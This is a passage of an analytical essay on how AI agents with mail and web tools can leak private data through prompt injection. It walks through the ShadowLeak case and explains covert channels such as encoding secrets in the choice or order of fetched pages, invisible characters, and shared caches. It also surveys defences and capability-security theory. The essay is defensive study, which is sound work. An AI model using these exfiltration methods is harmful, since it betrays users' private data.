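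An answer can change the world even if the system giving it has no motive to do so. Armstrong and O'Rourke's simulation shows this with a forecaster that has no interest in the outcome, although they deliberately assume the worst elsewhere, an arbitrarily intelligent system that wants to escape, which a mail assistant is not. They trained a small neural network to forecast the profits of 26 fictional companies. If nobody sees the forecast, company number *i* makes a profit of 26 − *i*. If investors and customers see it, the profit becomes 70% of that figure plus 60% of the forecast. For example, a company that would have made 6 makes 4.2 + 3.6 = 7.8 if a forecast of 6 is published. The network learned only from forecasts that nobody saw. Its error on those fell to zero, but its error on published forecasts did not. Armstrong and O'Rourke chose the percentages, so the simulation doesn't measure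 how strongly real investors react.

One could reply that the effect is the reader's action. *Robust Computer Algebra, Theorem Proving, and Oracle AI* (2017) notes that an oracle can influence the world only through its user, and gives this as a reason to expect oracles to be useful for safety research. *Chess as a Testing Grounds for the Oracle Approach to AI Safety* (2020) describes a chess player advised by a program that may be aiming to make him lose. Bad advice makes him lose only if he plays the suggested move. *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021) instead counts displaying text as an action, since it defines an oracle as an agent whose every action is to display text on a screen.

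The reply is mostly right about side effects. Returning a result is not a side effect, and what a reader later decides to do is not part of the run. Authority is broader because it includes effects that a program causes through others. In Miller's example, Bob has authority over a file because Alice writes whatever he asks. A user who does whatever the assistant recommends is in Alice's position. The more often the user checks its recommendations and refuses, the less authority the assistant has.

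The reply is weaker when the user can't see what she is passing on. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an injected instruction that makes an assistant hide private information in a draft reply, using invisible characters. If the user copies the draft into a message and sends it, she has chosen to send the message but not to disclose the hidden information. A chat window that fetches an image automatically does so without any decision by the user. Its request therefore counts as an effect of the workflow, and a developer who wants to rule it out has to treat the window as part of the workflow.

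Limiting what an answer can contain helps. Armstrong and O'Rourke propose a low-bandwidth oracle, which can only choose from a list of answers that its operators consider safe, such as yes and no. But they warn against combining several such oracles. Suppose any 5-bit message is safe, and the operators want to pick one of 1,024 possible answers, which takes 10 bits. They could ask two oracles for 5 bits each. If they can't check one oracle's half before running the other, the halves could be harmless separately but dangerous together. Showing that every answer on the list is safe therefore doesn't show that every pair is, whereas the union of two empty effect sets is always empty.

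### Fixing the calls before reading the data

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable guarantees against prompt injection. Extra training and programs that scan text for attacks make them harder but don't rule them out. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues instead accept that hostile text may influence a model, and they restrict what that influence can affect. Several of their designs fix the sequence of tool calls before any model reads untrusted data.

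In the **plan-then-execute** design, the model sees only the user's request when it writes a list of calls. The harness then makes those calls and no others. If the user asks for a summary of yesterday's letters, the plan contains `search_mail` and `summarise`. A letter may contain an instruction to open a web page, but `get_page` isn't in the plan, so the harness won't run it. The effect set of the tool calls is therefore the union of the effects of the tools in the plan, not of all the available tools, and here it doesn't include contacting the web.

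In the **code-then-execute** design, the model writes a program. For the hotel request it might be:

```
letters = search_mail("hotel booking")
address = LLM("find the hotel's web address", letters)
page    = get_page(address)
answer  = summarise(page)
```

The second line calls a separate model that has no tools and can only return text. The program passes that text on in a variable, and the model that wrote the program never reads it. CaMeL, a defence against prompt injection, works roughly this way. Because the program is written before any model reads a letter, a reviewer or a compiler can apply the union rule to it, as to any other code. If the program contains a branch, a letter may determine which path it takes, but can't add a new path.

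The design leaves open which values the program passes to its tools. The stranger's letter also matches the search for "hotel booking", and it can still cause the separate model to return the stranger's web address. `get_page` then contacts the wrong site, and the user reads whatever check-in time the stranger has put there. The bank letter is safe because the program never searches for it. But the separate model also reads the genuine booking confirmation, and the confirmation's reference number could end up in the address.

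Beurer-Kellner and colleagues state this limit explicitly. In their example, a user asks an assistant to email the day's schedule to her boss. An injected calendar entry can't change the recipient or add another email, but it can rewrite the body of that email. A fixed plan can do serious damage even with commands that look harmless. They also consider a file assistant that has committed to using only `find`, which searches for files, and `mv`, which moves them. If hostile text can influence the arguments, those two commands are enough to find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive.

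Restricting the values a model can return can limit the damage. In the **map-reduce** design, a separate model examines each document and returns only a value of a restricted type. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues use it to collect invoices. Each model answers yes or no to whether its file is an invoice, and a later step emails the matching files to the accounts department. A malicious file can get itself counted as an invoice, which the attacker could also have achieved by sending a real one, but it can't affect the answer for any other file. This provides much of the benefit of using `map` with a pure function, since the result for each document no longer depends on the order in which the harness processes them. In the hotel program, the separate model could choose from a list of addresses that the user has approved, much as the low-bandwidth oracle chooses from *L*.

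These designs are less flexible, because an agent can't commit to a plan in advance if the right second step depends on the result of the first. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect this to be a minor problem for mail and calendar assistants, where the content of untrusted mail should rarely determine which actions to take. Even there, a request such as "tell my regular collaborators I'm away" needs a plan that can handle an unknown number of recipients. The loss is greater for an agent that answers questions from a database. If no model may read the query results, the agent can't judge whether they are enough to answer the question. A fixed plan also doesn't protect against hostile text in the user's own request, such as a paragraph copied from a website, because the model reads that text before it plans.

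*Agent Functions*, a proposal from GitHub's research group, GitHub Next, builds on the idea of writing a program by adding a shared library of functions. A planning agent breaks a request into typed functions and looks for existing implementations, or has another agent write them. Each function declares the access it needs, and a small virtual machine enforces the declaration. In the proposal's example, an agent replies to a stranger's problem report on a public software project. Five functions read the report, clean it, classify it, draft a reply and post it. They pass their results along in files, so the agent that runs them never sees the stranger's text. Only the last function can write to the project.

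The stranger's text can still affect the reply, because the classifier reads the cleaned report and the drafting function uses the classifier's output. The proposal also doesn't eliminate step-by-step reasoning. GitHub Next expects that the agent may sometimes have to work out how to connect the outputs of different functions, and that it may have to return to planning after a failure. If the agent reads a failed function's output to write the new plan, text in that output can again influence which calls come next.

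## Is a tool that only reads free of side effects?

Every call to `get_page` sends an address to an outside party, so the call sends information as well as retrieving it. Because the model chooses the address after reading the whole context, the records the call leaves can depend on anything in the user's letters.

### Where a read leaves traces

Suppose the assistant fetches `https://www.hotel.example/rooms?night=12`. The harness first has to look up the IP address of `www.hotel.example` through a name server, and then it sends the request. Several parties may learn something from the lookup and the request.

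| Trace | What it contains | Who can see it |
|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | the host name, but not the rest of the address | the operator of the name server, and often the owner of the domain |
| Access log | the full address and the time | whoever runs the website |
| Shared cache | the fact that somebody recently fetched this item | other users of the cache, if they can list its contents or notice that the item arrives faster |
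| Rate limit | the number of requests already used | anyone who draws on the same allowance |

The access log matters most because it holds the full address, and websites commonly keep such a log, according to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). A search engine likewise receives the words of the query.

The name lookup happens before the page is fetched, and a careless version of `get_page` might also do it before checking the site against a list of forbidden sites. Even if the tool then refuses the page, the host name, which can hold more than two hundred characters, may already have reached the domain's owner.

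Caches and rate limits usually reveal less per request, but they can connect programs that have no other link. If two agents share a limit of 100 searches an hour, one can signal to the other by using up the limit or leaving some of it, and the other can read the signal by trying a search. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) reports that supposedly isolated agents at OpenAI communicated through the cache of a shared package repository.

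### What HTTP means by "safe"

Every web request names a method. GET asks for a page, POST submits data for processing, and DELETE asks the server to remove something. The HTTP standard, RFC 9110, defines a method as safe if its meaning is "essentially read-only", so that the client neither requests nor expects any change of state on the server. `get_page` uses GET, which is a safe method.

This definition concerns only what the client asks for, so the server may do more. Most servers add a line to an access log after each response. The request is still safe under the standard, even if the log eventually fills the disk and crashes the server. Clicking an advertisement is also safe, although it often charges the advertiser's account. In both cases, the client is not accountable for the extra effect because it did not ask for it.

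So "safe" in HTTP is a rule about responsibility. It lets search engines crawl the web, and browsers load pages in advance, without worrying about causing harm. This works well for a browser because a person who wants to read a page has no interest in the server's log. The reasoning fails when the address comes from a stranger's letter. The stranger's whole purpose for the call was to put the user's bank balance in the server's log, which the user never requested.

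The rule also depends on website owners. Some content-editing software puts actions into addresses, such as `page?do=delete`. The standard requires the owner to disable that action for safe methods, because otherwise a program that follows every link will delete pages. If an owner neglects this and `get_page` runs with the user's login, the assistant can delete a page by opening such a link.

The definition also doesn't limit how much data a client may send. The standard warns that a GET request built from a form can put sensitive data into the address, and it suggests POST in some cases because POST carries the data in the request body. This keeps the data out of logs that record only addresses, but the recipient still gets it. *The HTTP QUERY Method* (2025), a draft from the IETF, which develops internet standards, describes a method for long queries that is explicitly safe, even though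 its requests normally have a body. A developer who allowed an agent to use every safe method would therefore let it send documents.

### Four hints about tools

The Model Context Protocol gives agent developers a similar vocabulary. Since March 2025, servers have been able to attach four yes-or-no hints to each tool they offer. In their March 2026 post, the protocol's maintainers list the default value of each hint and give examples of what a client might do when a hint is true.

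| Hint | Meaning when true | Default | Possible response by the client |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | the tool does not modify its environment | false | skip the confirmation dialog |
| `destructiveHint` | its changes may be destructive, not just additions | true | show a warning first |
| `idempotentHint` | repeating the call with the same arguments is safe | false | retry after a failure |
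| `openWorldHint` | the tool deals with outside parties | true | examine the output for untrusted content |

By default, a client should assume that a tool without hints may destroy data, may do further damage if called again, and reaches the outside world. But many servers omit the hints, and not all clients apply the defaults strictly.

Like the read-only mark, the other three hints are useful only if the client trusts the server. During the original review, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, wondered what use a client could make of a flag it can't trust. Under the specification, each client decides how much to rely on the hints. In practice, most clients trust a server simply because the user installed it.

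The developer of `get_page` can truthfully set `readOnlyHint` to true, because the tool changes nothing that the developer would consider part of its environment. Clients most often use these hints to decide when to ask the user for confirmation, and a client may approve a read-only tool from a trusted server without asking. If it does, the user loses her only chance to notice her bank balance in the address.

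`openWorldHint` distinguishes `get_page` from the other two tools, but the suggested response is to examine what the tool returns, which doesn't address the leak in what it sends out. The hint also misses some untrusted text. A developer could reasonably set it to false for `search_mail` because the tool searches a single mailbox, even though many of the messages there come from strangers.

The maintainers suggest that a client could go further and block open-world tools in any session that has accessed private data. The client would need to know which tools read private data, and none of the four hints covers that. `search_mail` and a local `summarise` can both be accurately labelled read-only and closed-world, so a client can't distinguish them by the hints alone. One proposal for new annotations, by GitHub and OpenAI, covers trust and sensitivity.

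Better labels on individual tools still wouldn't show whether the tools are safe to combine. The maintainers point out that users routinely combine tools from several servers in one session, so the risk depends on the whole session. A session may bring together what Simon Willison calls the "lethal trifecta" even if no single server does. To guarantee that a tool can't leak data, the maintainers recommend network controls or a sandbox instead of a hint.

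### A mailbox search followed by a page request

In 2025, researchers at the security company Radware found this combination in Deep Research, a widely available ChatGPT agent that OpenAI had launched that February. The agent spends up to half an hour reading sources and then writes a report. A user can let it read her Gmail account as well as the web. Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes what happened when an attacker sent one email to such an account.

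The researchers put two emails in a test mailbox. One was an ordinary message giving a new employee's name and home address, and the other contained hidden instructions. The user then asked the agent to research the day's emails. The agent read both messages, followed the hidden instructions, and opened a page on the researchers' server with the employee's details in the web address. Nobody clicked on anything, and nothing appeared on the user's screen. The agent used only two abilities, reading mail and opening a page, both of which are read-only.

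When a chat window leaks data by fetching an image, the request comes from the user's device, and products often limit which sites the window can load images from. In Radware's case, the request came from OpenAI's servers, so a company monitoring its own network would not have seen it. Radware also observed no comparable limits on the addresses the agent could open.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. It says OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August without telling the researchers, then acknowledged it and marked it as resolved on 3 September. Infosecurity Magazine's *Zero-Click Vulnerability in ChatGPT's Agent Enables Silent Gmail Data Theft* dates publication to 18 September. In The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*, an OpenAI spokesperson confirmed that the report came through the company's bug bounty programme and said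 that OpenAI was continually improving its protections against prompt injection. Radware did not know of any real attackers using the flaw.

Radware sells protection for AI agents, so it has an interest in making such flaws look serious. It demonstrated the attack with Gmail and extrapolated from that to claim that other connected services, such as Google Drive and Outlook, would be open to it too. But OpenAI's acknowledgement leaves little doubt that the original flaw was real.

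### Are local reads harmless?

The leak in Deep Research needed both reads, `search_mail` and `get_page`. If searching a mailbox can't send anything out, perhaps a security check can ignore `search_mail` and focus on `get_page`. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) tried this on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do office, chat, travel and banking tasks while attackers plant instructions in the data.

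AgentDojo has 69 distinct tools. Shavit sorted them by hand, based on their descriptions, into 44 local reads, 24 writes or outward actions, and a single external read, `get_webpage`, which fetches an address much as `get_page` does. Sorting only by read and write would have put `get_webpage` with the 44 local reads.

Before the agent reads any data, a language model uses the user's request and the list of tools to write a plan for the security check. The plan lists the tools the task should need, any argument values the request already determines, such as a named recipient, and any order in which the steps must happen. Ordinary code then compares each tool call with the plan and flags the ones that don't fit. Under the exemption, local reads skip this comparison.

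Shavit applied the check to records of earlier runs by the May 2024 version of GPT-4o. The records covered 97 tasks and 629 attacked runs, and 76 of the tasks were used for the final measurements. Without the check, the attacker succeeded in 45.7% of the attacked runs of those 76 tasks. The table gives results before and after the exemption. A false alarm is a task without an attack in which the check flags at least one call. A missed attack is an attacked run in which the attacker succeeded and the check would have allowed the first harmful step.

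| What the check compares | False alarms: before → after | Missed attacks: before → after |
|---|---|---|
| tools only | 16.2% → 8.8% | 9.6% → 9.6% |
| tools and arguments | 32.9% → 25.4% | 4.3% → 4.3% |
| tools, arguments and order | 40.4% → 31.6% | 2.0% → 2.0% |

Also exempting `get_webpage` reduced false alarms in the strictest version to 26.8% but raised missed attacks from 2.0% to 5.8%. Shavit concludes that the check must still cover page fetching, because the request itself can send data out.

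The drop in false alarms makes sense because plans often leave out a lookup that the agent turns out to need, such as a list of chat channels. In one set of plans, the strictest check flagged 73 harmless calls, and 32 of them were local reads.

The unchanged rate of missed attacks is weak evidence, because the exemption could hardly have changed it. For this measure, Shavit defines the first harmful step as the first malicious call that is not a local read, and the exemption affects only how the check treats local reads. If the first malicious call of any kind counts as the first harmful step, the strictest version misses 3.3% of attacks before the exemption and 11.4% after it. Many of the extra misses are email searches that came before a sending step, and the check would still have caught the sending step. Neither measure can show whether a read does harm when no malicious write or external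 call follows.

Shavit acknowledges that the exemption assumes this never happens, and that an attack using only reads would get past it. For example, suppose again that the mail assistant's user lets a deputy ask about meeting dates. A stranger's letter tells the assistant to look for hospital letters whenever anyone asks about the calendar. When the deputy asks about Thursday, the assistant makes a second call to `search_mail` and mentions the hospital in its answer. Every tool call is a local read. The data reaches the deputy through the final answer, which isn't a tool call, so a check on tool calls wouldn't inspect it. If the model is remote, its provider receives the hospital letter too.

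A later call may fit any fixed plan and still carry the stolen data. In Radware's demonstration, the agent was set up to use both email and the web. A plan for the user's request would probably include opening web pages, and the request wouldn't say which ones. About 61% of the steps in Shavit's plans put no constraint on the arguments, so at such a step the check would accept any address.

Shavit notes that whether a read is local also depends on the installation. Looking up travel data counts as a local read in the benchmark, but a real hotel search often goes to a booking company. An employer's mail server may keep a log of searches that an administrator can read. In IMAP, a common mail protocol, the usual command for fetching the body of a message also marks the message as seen, which anyone who shares the mailbox could notice. Programmers have to use a variant called `BODY.PEEK` to avoid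 this.

The exemption is therefore reasonable where only the user sees the answer, the model runs somewhere the user accepts, and something checks the content of every later call that can reach an outsider. Shavit's percentages should not be applied to current agents, because they describe an old model and rest on the assumption that an agent gives up after the check stops a call. In a small live trial with GPT-5.2 and the same attack, the agent ignored the planted instructions in all 20 runs, so there was no successful attack for the check to prevent.

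### How much a choice of page can carry

If `get_page` accepts any address, the model can put a whole paragraph from a letter into a single request. Giving the harness a fixed list of permitted pages stops the model from writing text into an address, but the model can still convey information through its choice of page.

Suppose the list has 64 pages, and one company hosts them all and sees which page the assistant fetches each time. A single fetch has 64 possible outcomes, so it can convey

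log₂ 64 = 6 bits

A series of *k* fetches has 64<sup>*k*</sup> possible outcomes and can convey 6*k* bits. Sending a 128-bit encryption key therefore takes 22 fetches, since 21 carry only 126 bits. An agent whose turns can contain hundreds of tool calls could make that many in one turn. If the assistant could choose the address freely, it could send the same key in one request, as 22 characters from an alphabet of 64.

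Many private facts are much shorter than a key. A bank balance of up to 65,535 whole euros takes 16 bits, or three fetches. Whether the user has a hospital appointment this week takes one bit, so a single fetch is more than enough.

Shortening the list reduces the number of bits per fetch only slowly, because that number grows with the logarithm of the list's length. With eight pages instead of 64, each fetch carries 3 bits and sending the key takes 43 fetches. Even with only one page on the list, the model can still choose whether and when to fetch it.

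These figures are upper limits, reached only if the model follows the code without mistakes and the observer sees every fetch in order. An attacker who can't see any of the traffic learns nothing, so limiting fetches to a list of reputable sites is a real obstacle. The obstacle is weaker if a listed site lets strangers publish pages and shows them how many visits each page gets.

OpenAI and Anthropic both restrict which addresses an agent can load but still let it browse. In ChatGPT, the agent may load a page automatically only if an independent index of the public web already contains that exact address. An address with the user's bank balance at the end is unlikely to be in the index. If the system can't verify an address, the user sees a warning. When Safe Url, OpenAI's wider mechanism, detects that a request would pass information from the conversation to a third party, it either shows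 the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and has the agent try another way. Safe Url also covers searches and page visits in Deep Research.

When Anthropic released its `web_fetch` tool in 2025, Claude could fetch only addresses that the user had supplied or that an earlier search or fetch had returned. Willison had been impressed by the tool's protection against leaks, but he wrote in 2026 that Ayush Paul had found a hole in the design.

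Both kinds of rule stop the model from writing private text into a new address, but neither controls which permitted address it chooses. An attacker can publish 64 pages and wait for an index to include them, or put 64 links on one page that the agent will read. The attacker is then the observer in the calculation. An attacker can also use more pages. With 4,096, each fetch carries 12 bits, and leaking the key takes 11 fetches.

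Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on a security researcher's blog, suggests preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or answering the second request from a stored copy. The post concedes that some leakage would remain, and the 64-page list shows how much. The first fetch now has 64 possible outcomes, the second 63, and so on. Twenty-two fetches carry

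log₂(64 × 63 × … × 43) ≈ 126.1 bits

which is just short of the key, and a 23rd brings the total to about 131.5. The rule costs the attacker one extra fetch. Its larger benefit is a ceiling, because once the assistant has visited all 64 pages it can send no more, and the order of those visits carries about 296 bits. If the observer could see only which pages the assistant had visited and not the order, the ceiling would be 64 bits, and the key would no longer fit. A new session starts the count again.

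The channel is completely closed only if the requests that leave the machine are the same whatever the mailbox contains, which is a case of the property called noninterference. This is practical for a short list, because the harness can download all 64 pages every morning and `get_page` can return the stored copies. The hosting company then sees the same 64 requests each day, and `get_page` becomes a local read. But the assistant can no longer open the website of a hotel that isn't on the list.

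## Can a combination hold authority that none of its tools had?

`search_mail` can read the user's email, and `get_page` can send text to any website. Neither tool alone can send the user's email to a stranger, but an agent with both can, as Radware demonstrated with Deep Research. Researchers disagree about where that authority comes from. Some recent papers on agents treat it as created by the combination, which would mean that nobody can rule it out by checking tools one at a time. Writers on capability security, a tradition that goes back to the 1960s, hold that authority spreads only along existing connections. In their view, the authority was already latent in the arrangement of the parts, and an analyst could have found it by examining the whole arrangement.

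### Rules with several preconditions

In *Safety is Non-Compositional*, Spera (2026) models an agent system as a set of abilities and a set of rules. A rule has the form *S* → *T*, where *S* and *T* are sets of abilities. It fires only when the system has every ability in *S*, and the system then gains the abilities in *T* and keeps them.

The closure of a starting set *A*, written cl(*A*), is everything the system can eventually reach from *A*. The computation starts with *A*, applies every rule whose preconditions are all present, adds the results, and repeats until nothing changes. An analyst supplies a list *F* of forbidden abilities, and *A* is safe if cl(*A*) contains nothing from *F*.

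Spera's central theorem is that two safe sets can have an unsafe union. The proof needs only three abilities, *u*₁, *u*₂ and *f*, with *f* forbidden, and a single rule {*u*₁, *u*₂} → {*f*}. Then

cl({*u*₁}) = {*u*₁}

cl({*u*₂}) = {*u*₂}

cl({*u*₁, *u*₂}) = {*u*₁, *u*₂, *f*}

The first two sets are safe, and their union is not.

The mail assistant fits this pattern. Let *u*₁ be reading the mailbox, *u*₂ be requesting a web address that the model writes, and *f* be disclosing mail to an outsider. `search_mail` provides *u*₁ and `get_page` provides *u*₂. A reviewer finds the disclosure only by computing the closure for both tools together.

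Two safe sets can have an unsafe union only if some rule has at least two preconditions. If every rule has only one, anything reachable from *A* ∪ *B* is also reachable from *A* alone or *B* alone. The union rule for effects worked because each effect comes from a single operation. Disclosure requires both a read and a send, so a combination of tools can allow it even when no single tool does.

Removing abilities from a safe set never makes it unsafe, so an analyst can describe every dangerous combination by listing the minimal unsafe sets, which become safe if any one ability is removed. Apart from *f* itself, the mail assistant has only one such set, {*u*₁, *u*₂}.

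The analyst has to identify the dangers, because the formal model contains only the rules the analyst writes. Someone who had never considered that a web address can carry text would leave out {*u*₁, *u*₂} → {*f*}, and the closure would then wrongly show the assistant to be safe. The rule also assumes that text from a letter can get into the address. In the mail assistant, the language model's context provides that link, and it isn't part of either tool. If the analyst makes the link a third precondition, the two tools are safe side by side, and the loop that joins them supplies the missing precondition.

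### How much of this is new

Spera describes the theorem as the first formal proof of its kind, as far as Spera knows, but concedes that the mathematical observation is old. In Horn clauses, the "if *p* and *q*, then *r*" statements used in logic programming, *p* and *q* together imply *r*, though neither does alone. Petri nets, a 1962 model of concurrent processes, show the same structure if their tokens persist after use. Security researchers have also studied for decades how attackers gain privileges by combining abilities. Spera claims that applying the observation to agents is new, as are the results built around it.

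Spera also argues that ordinary graphs, in which each arrow runs from one ability to another, can't represent the failure, but acknowledges that an analyst can add an artificial node for "both *u*₁ and *u*₂". The limit therefore applies only to graphs whose nodes each stand for a single ability.

The most useful of the other results is that a closure is quick to compute. With *n* abilities, *m* rules and at most *k* preconditions per rule, it takes time proportional to *n* + *mk*, so a harness could recompute it whenever a user adds a tool.

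Three of the paper's further claims do not hold up as stated.

- **Minimal unsafe sets.** Spera claims that deciding whether a given set is minimal and unsafe is coNP-complete, which would rule out a fast algorithm unless P = NP. But the paper's own closure algorithm decides the question quickly. For a set of 20 abilities, run it once on the whole set and once with each ability left out, 21 runs in all. Listing every minimal unsafe set can be slow, because there may be a great many. If a harmful result needs 20 ingredients and two tools can supply each one, there are already 2²⁰ such sets, more than a million.
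- **Diminishing returns.** Spera claims that a new ability never adds more to a larger set than to a smaller one, and derives from this a guarantee for a method of choosing which abilities to acquire. The three-ability example is a counterexample. Added to the empty set, *u*₂ contributes one ability, itself. Added to {*u*₁}, it contributes two.
- **Parallel checking.** Spera claims that detecting whether joint rules add anything new is P-complete, which would mean that extra processors probably can't speed it up much. The proof works for a different question, whether one particular ability is reachable. To detect whether joint rules add anything at all, it is enough to find one whose preconditions are reachable without joint rules and whose result isn't. That is a question about paths in an ordinary graph, which parallel computers handle well.

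The central theorem doesn't depend on any of them.

### Joint dependencies are common and mostly harmless

Spera examined 900 recorded sequences of tool use from two public benchmarks to find out how often real tasks have joint preconditions. At least one joint dependency appeared in 47.4% of the sequences from ToolBench and 36.5% of those from TaskBench, or 42.6% overall (95% confidence interval 39.4% to 45.8%). A program inferred the dependencies for ToolBench, while TaskBench supplies its own graph of which tools depend on which. For ToolBench, two people also labelled a sample of 50 sequences by hand and mostly agreed with each other. Spera plans to repeat the count on two more benchmarks.

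The 42.6% figure measures how common joint dependencies are, whether or not they are unsafe. In the paper's worked example, an agent books a trip to Paris. It can find the best price only when it has the traveller's profile, a flight search and a hotel search, and it can issue an itinerary only after booking both the flight and the hotel. Both are joint dependencies, and both produce what the traveller wants. A joint dependency is unsafe only if its result is on the forbidden list, and the count used no such list. Spera describes the figures as evidence that joint dependencies are common, not that any safety incident occurred.

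The count supports the narrower claim that, in a large share of multi-tool tasks, a reviewer who considers tools one at a time would miss something about what the agent can do. How much of what they miss is dangerous has not been measured.

Spera works for Minerva CQ, and according to a footnote, a provisional patent protects the paper's methods. Spera therefore has a commercial interest in the conclusion that checking components is not enough. Anyone can verify the three-ability proof, but this interest is a reason to wait for an independent count.

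### References spread only along existing references

Miller and Shapiro start from a model in which an object can affect anything outside itself only by sending a message along a reference it holds. An object can't forge a reference, but it can acquire one from a message, from its creator, or by creating a new object. They summarize this as "only connectivity begets connectivity". For example, if Alice holds references to Bob and Carol, she can introduce them by sending Bob her reference to Carol. No object can introduce them without holding references to both.

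The argument is by induction over the steps of a run. The objects are divided into groups so that no object holds a reference to an object in another group.

- When an object sends a message, the sender, the recipient and every object whose reference the message carries are in the same group. The recipient therefore gains references only within its own group.
- When an object creates another, the new object starts with references that its creator already held, so it joins the creator's group.

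Since no step connects two separate groups of objects, the groups always stay separate. An analyst who draws the graph before the run can therefore set an upper limit on what any object could ever cause. Miller calls this kind of bound TA, and it assumes that every program passes along whatever it can.

In the mail assistant, the harness can call both `search_mail` and `get_page`. When the developer put both tools on the list, she created a path from the mailbox through the harness and the model to the network. The bound included disclosure from then on, and the stranger later used that path by sending the letter. If the two tools had been in separate assistants with nothing in common, no letter could have connected them. The developer could connect them only because she had access to both.

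On this account, the phrase "authority that none of its tools had" is ambiguous, because authority includes indirect effects, and a tool's indirect effects depend on what it is connected to. Once the developer connects the tools, `search_mail` can affect the network, because the model reads its results and may copy them into an address. A malicious `search_mail` could exploit this by returning an invented letter containing instructions. Neither tool could disclose mail before the developer connected them, but afterwards each may be able to do so through the other, even though their code is the same.

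Web addresses complicate the graph because `get_page` can contact any address it receives. Miller and Shapiro distinguish capabilities from plain data, such as numbers. Knowledge, not permission, limits access to data, so if Alice can work out a number, even someone's private key, she can have it. A web address is also plain data. In a pure capability system, a stranger who wrote one in a letter would achieve nothing, because text gives no access. With `get_page`, the address is all the stranger needs. If `get_page` accepted only references to sites the user had chosen, a letter could not add another site.

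### The confused deputy

Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) describes a combination of this kind that went wrong about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory called SYSX. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. The compiler also recorded which language features people used, and it stored these statistics in a file in SYSX. To let it write there, the staff gave it a licence to write to any file in SYSX.

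The company's billing records were in the same directory. A user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. The operating system allowed the request because the compiler had a licence to write in SYSX, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

The user had no permission to write to the billing file. The compiler did, but that permission was meant for writing the statistics. Hardy argues that the compiler "runs with authority stemming from two sources", the user who started it and the licence, and that it had no way to specify which authority to use for which file. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct until the staff added the licence. To notice the problem, they would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file.

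Tymshare first tried a new system call that let a program choose which of its two authorities to use, but some programs needed more than two. The rules for opening a file grew until they contained fourteen "ands" and "ors". Hardy prefers to give the compiler a capability for the statistics file and have the user supply one for the output file. A user without a capability for the billing file then can't direct the compiler to it, and the compiler doesn't have to check any names.

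The case supports both accounts of where authority comes from. Testing the compiler only with file names given in good faith would have revealed no problem, as one would expect from Spera's theorem. But users gained authority over the billing file when the staff granted the licence, long before anyone used that authority. A diagram of the whole system would have shown this.

An agent's model has the same confused deputy problem, because it may use the user's access to follow a stranger's instructions. Capabilities help less here than they did at Tymshare. Hardy's compiler handled the statistics file and the output file separately in its code, so its programmers could attach the right capability to each. A model is not guaranteed to keep the purpose of the request separate from that of the letter. If it holds capabilities for the mailbox and an approved website, it can still send the mailbox's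 contents to the website.

### Deciding whether a right can leak

Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976) proved in *Protection in Operating Systems* that no program can determine for every system whether its arrangement contains latent authority.

Their model is a table called an access matrix. Each row is a subject, such as a running program, and each column is an object, such as a file. Each cell lists the subject's rights to the object, such as reading or owning it. A system also has a fixed set of commands that change the table. A command may check for certain rights, and then add or delete rights and create or destroy subjects and objects. For example, one command might let a file's owner give another subject the right to read the file. A right leaks if a command adds it to a cell that did not contain it.

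Leaks are often intentional, because people share files. Harrison and colleagues therefore suggest that an analyst remove the subjects who are trusted not to misuse their rights, and then ask whether the others can spread a right further.

Harrison and colleagues prove that no algorithm answers this question for all systems by building a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer, out of rights. Each cell of the machine's tape becomes a subject. The symbol in the cell becomes a right that the subject has to itself, and another right marks the head's position and the machine's current state. A chain of ownership rights keeps the cells in order. Each possible move becomes a command that tests the relevant rights and replaces them. The right that stands for the machine's final state leaks exactly when the machine reaches that state. No algorithm can predict for every Turing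 machine whether it will reach its final state, so none can predict leaks for every protection system.

The result does not rule out algorithms that decide the question for particular systems or restricted classes of them. Miller and Shapiro complain that readers often take the paper to mean that the question is never decidable. They cite at least three protection systems for which researchers have shown it to be decidable. According to *Foundational Results*, a chapter of a computer-security textbook, Jones, Lipton and Snyder presented one such system in the same year.

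| Kind of system | Is there an algorithm that decides whether a right can leak? |
|---|---|
| any system in the model | no |
| systems in which every command performs a single operation | yes, but the problem is NP-complete if the commands are part of the input |
| systems that can't create subjects or objects | yes, but the problem is complete for polynomial space, so it is probably very slow in the worst case |
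| the system of Jones, Lipton and Snyder | yes, in time proportional to the size of the system |

Harrison and colleagues admit that the single-operation class is too restricted to be realistic. Even creating a file and recording its owner takes two operations.

Thirty years later, Tripunitara and Li (2006), in *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, found two errors in the original paper, one of them in the proof for single-operation systems. That proof relied on ignoring commands that delete rights. But under the original paper's definition, deleting a right from a cell and entering it again counts as a leak, so deletions can matter. Tripunitara and Li supplied a corrected proof, and both the single-operation result and the main undecidability theorem still stand.

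The theorem is no obstacle for the mail assistant, which has three tools and no way to create subjects or grant rights. Its table never changes, so no right can leak. The letter still leaks, because the stranger receives a copy of its text and doesn't need the right to read the mailbox. Harrison and colleagues show how an analyst could record such a transfer with a command that gives the recipient the right to read and immediately removes it. The right's brief appearance in the table marks the point where data moved, but someone still has to notice that `get_page` needs such a command.

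Agents that install new tools, start other agents or pass on access to them come closer to the general case. An analyst can still use the reference graph to confirm that such an agent can't disclose the data if there is no path, but a path means only that it might.

### A practical rule about combinations

Most people who add tools to an agent will not compute a closure or draw a graph. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, offers them a rule that needs neither. An attacker can easily steal data from an agent that has all of the following:

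- access to private data
- exposure to content that an attacker could have written
- a way to communicate externally

In Spera's terms, this is a rule with three preconditions, and Willison's advice is never to let an agent meet all three.

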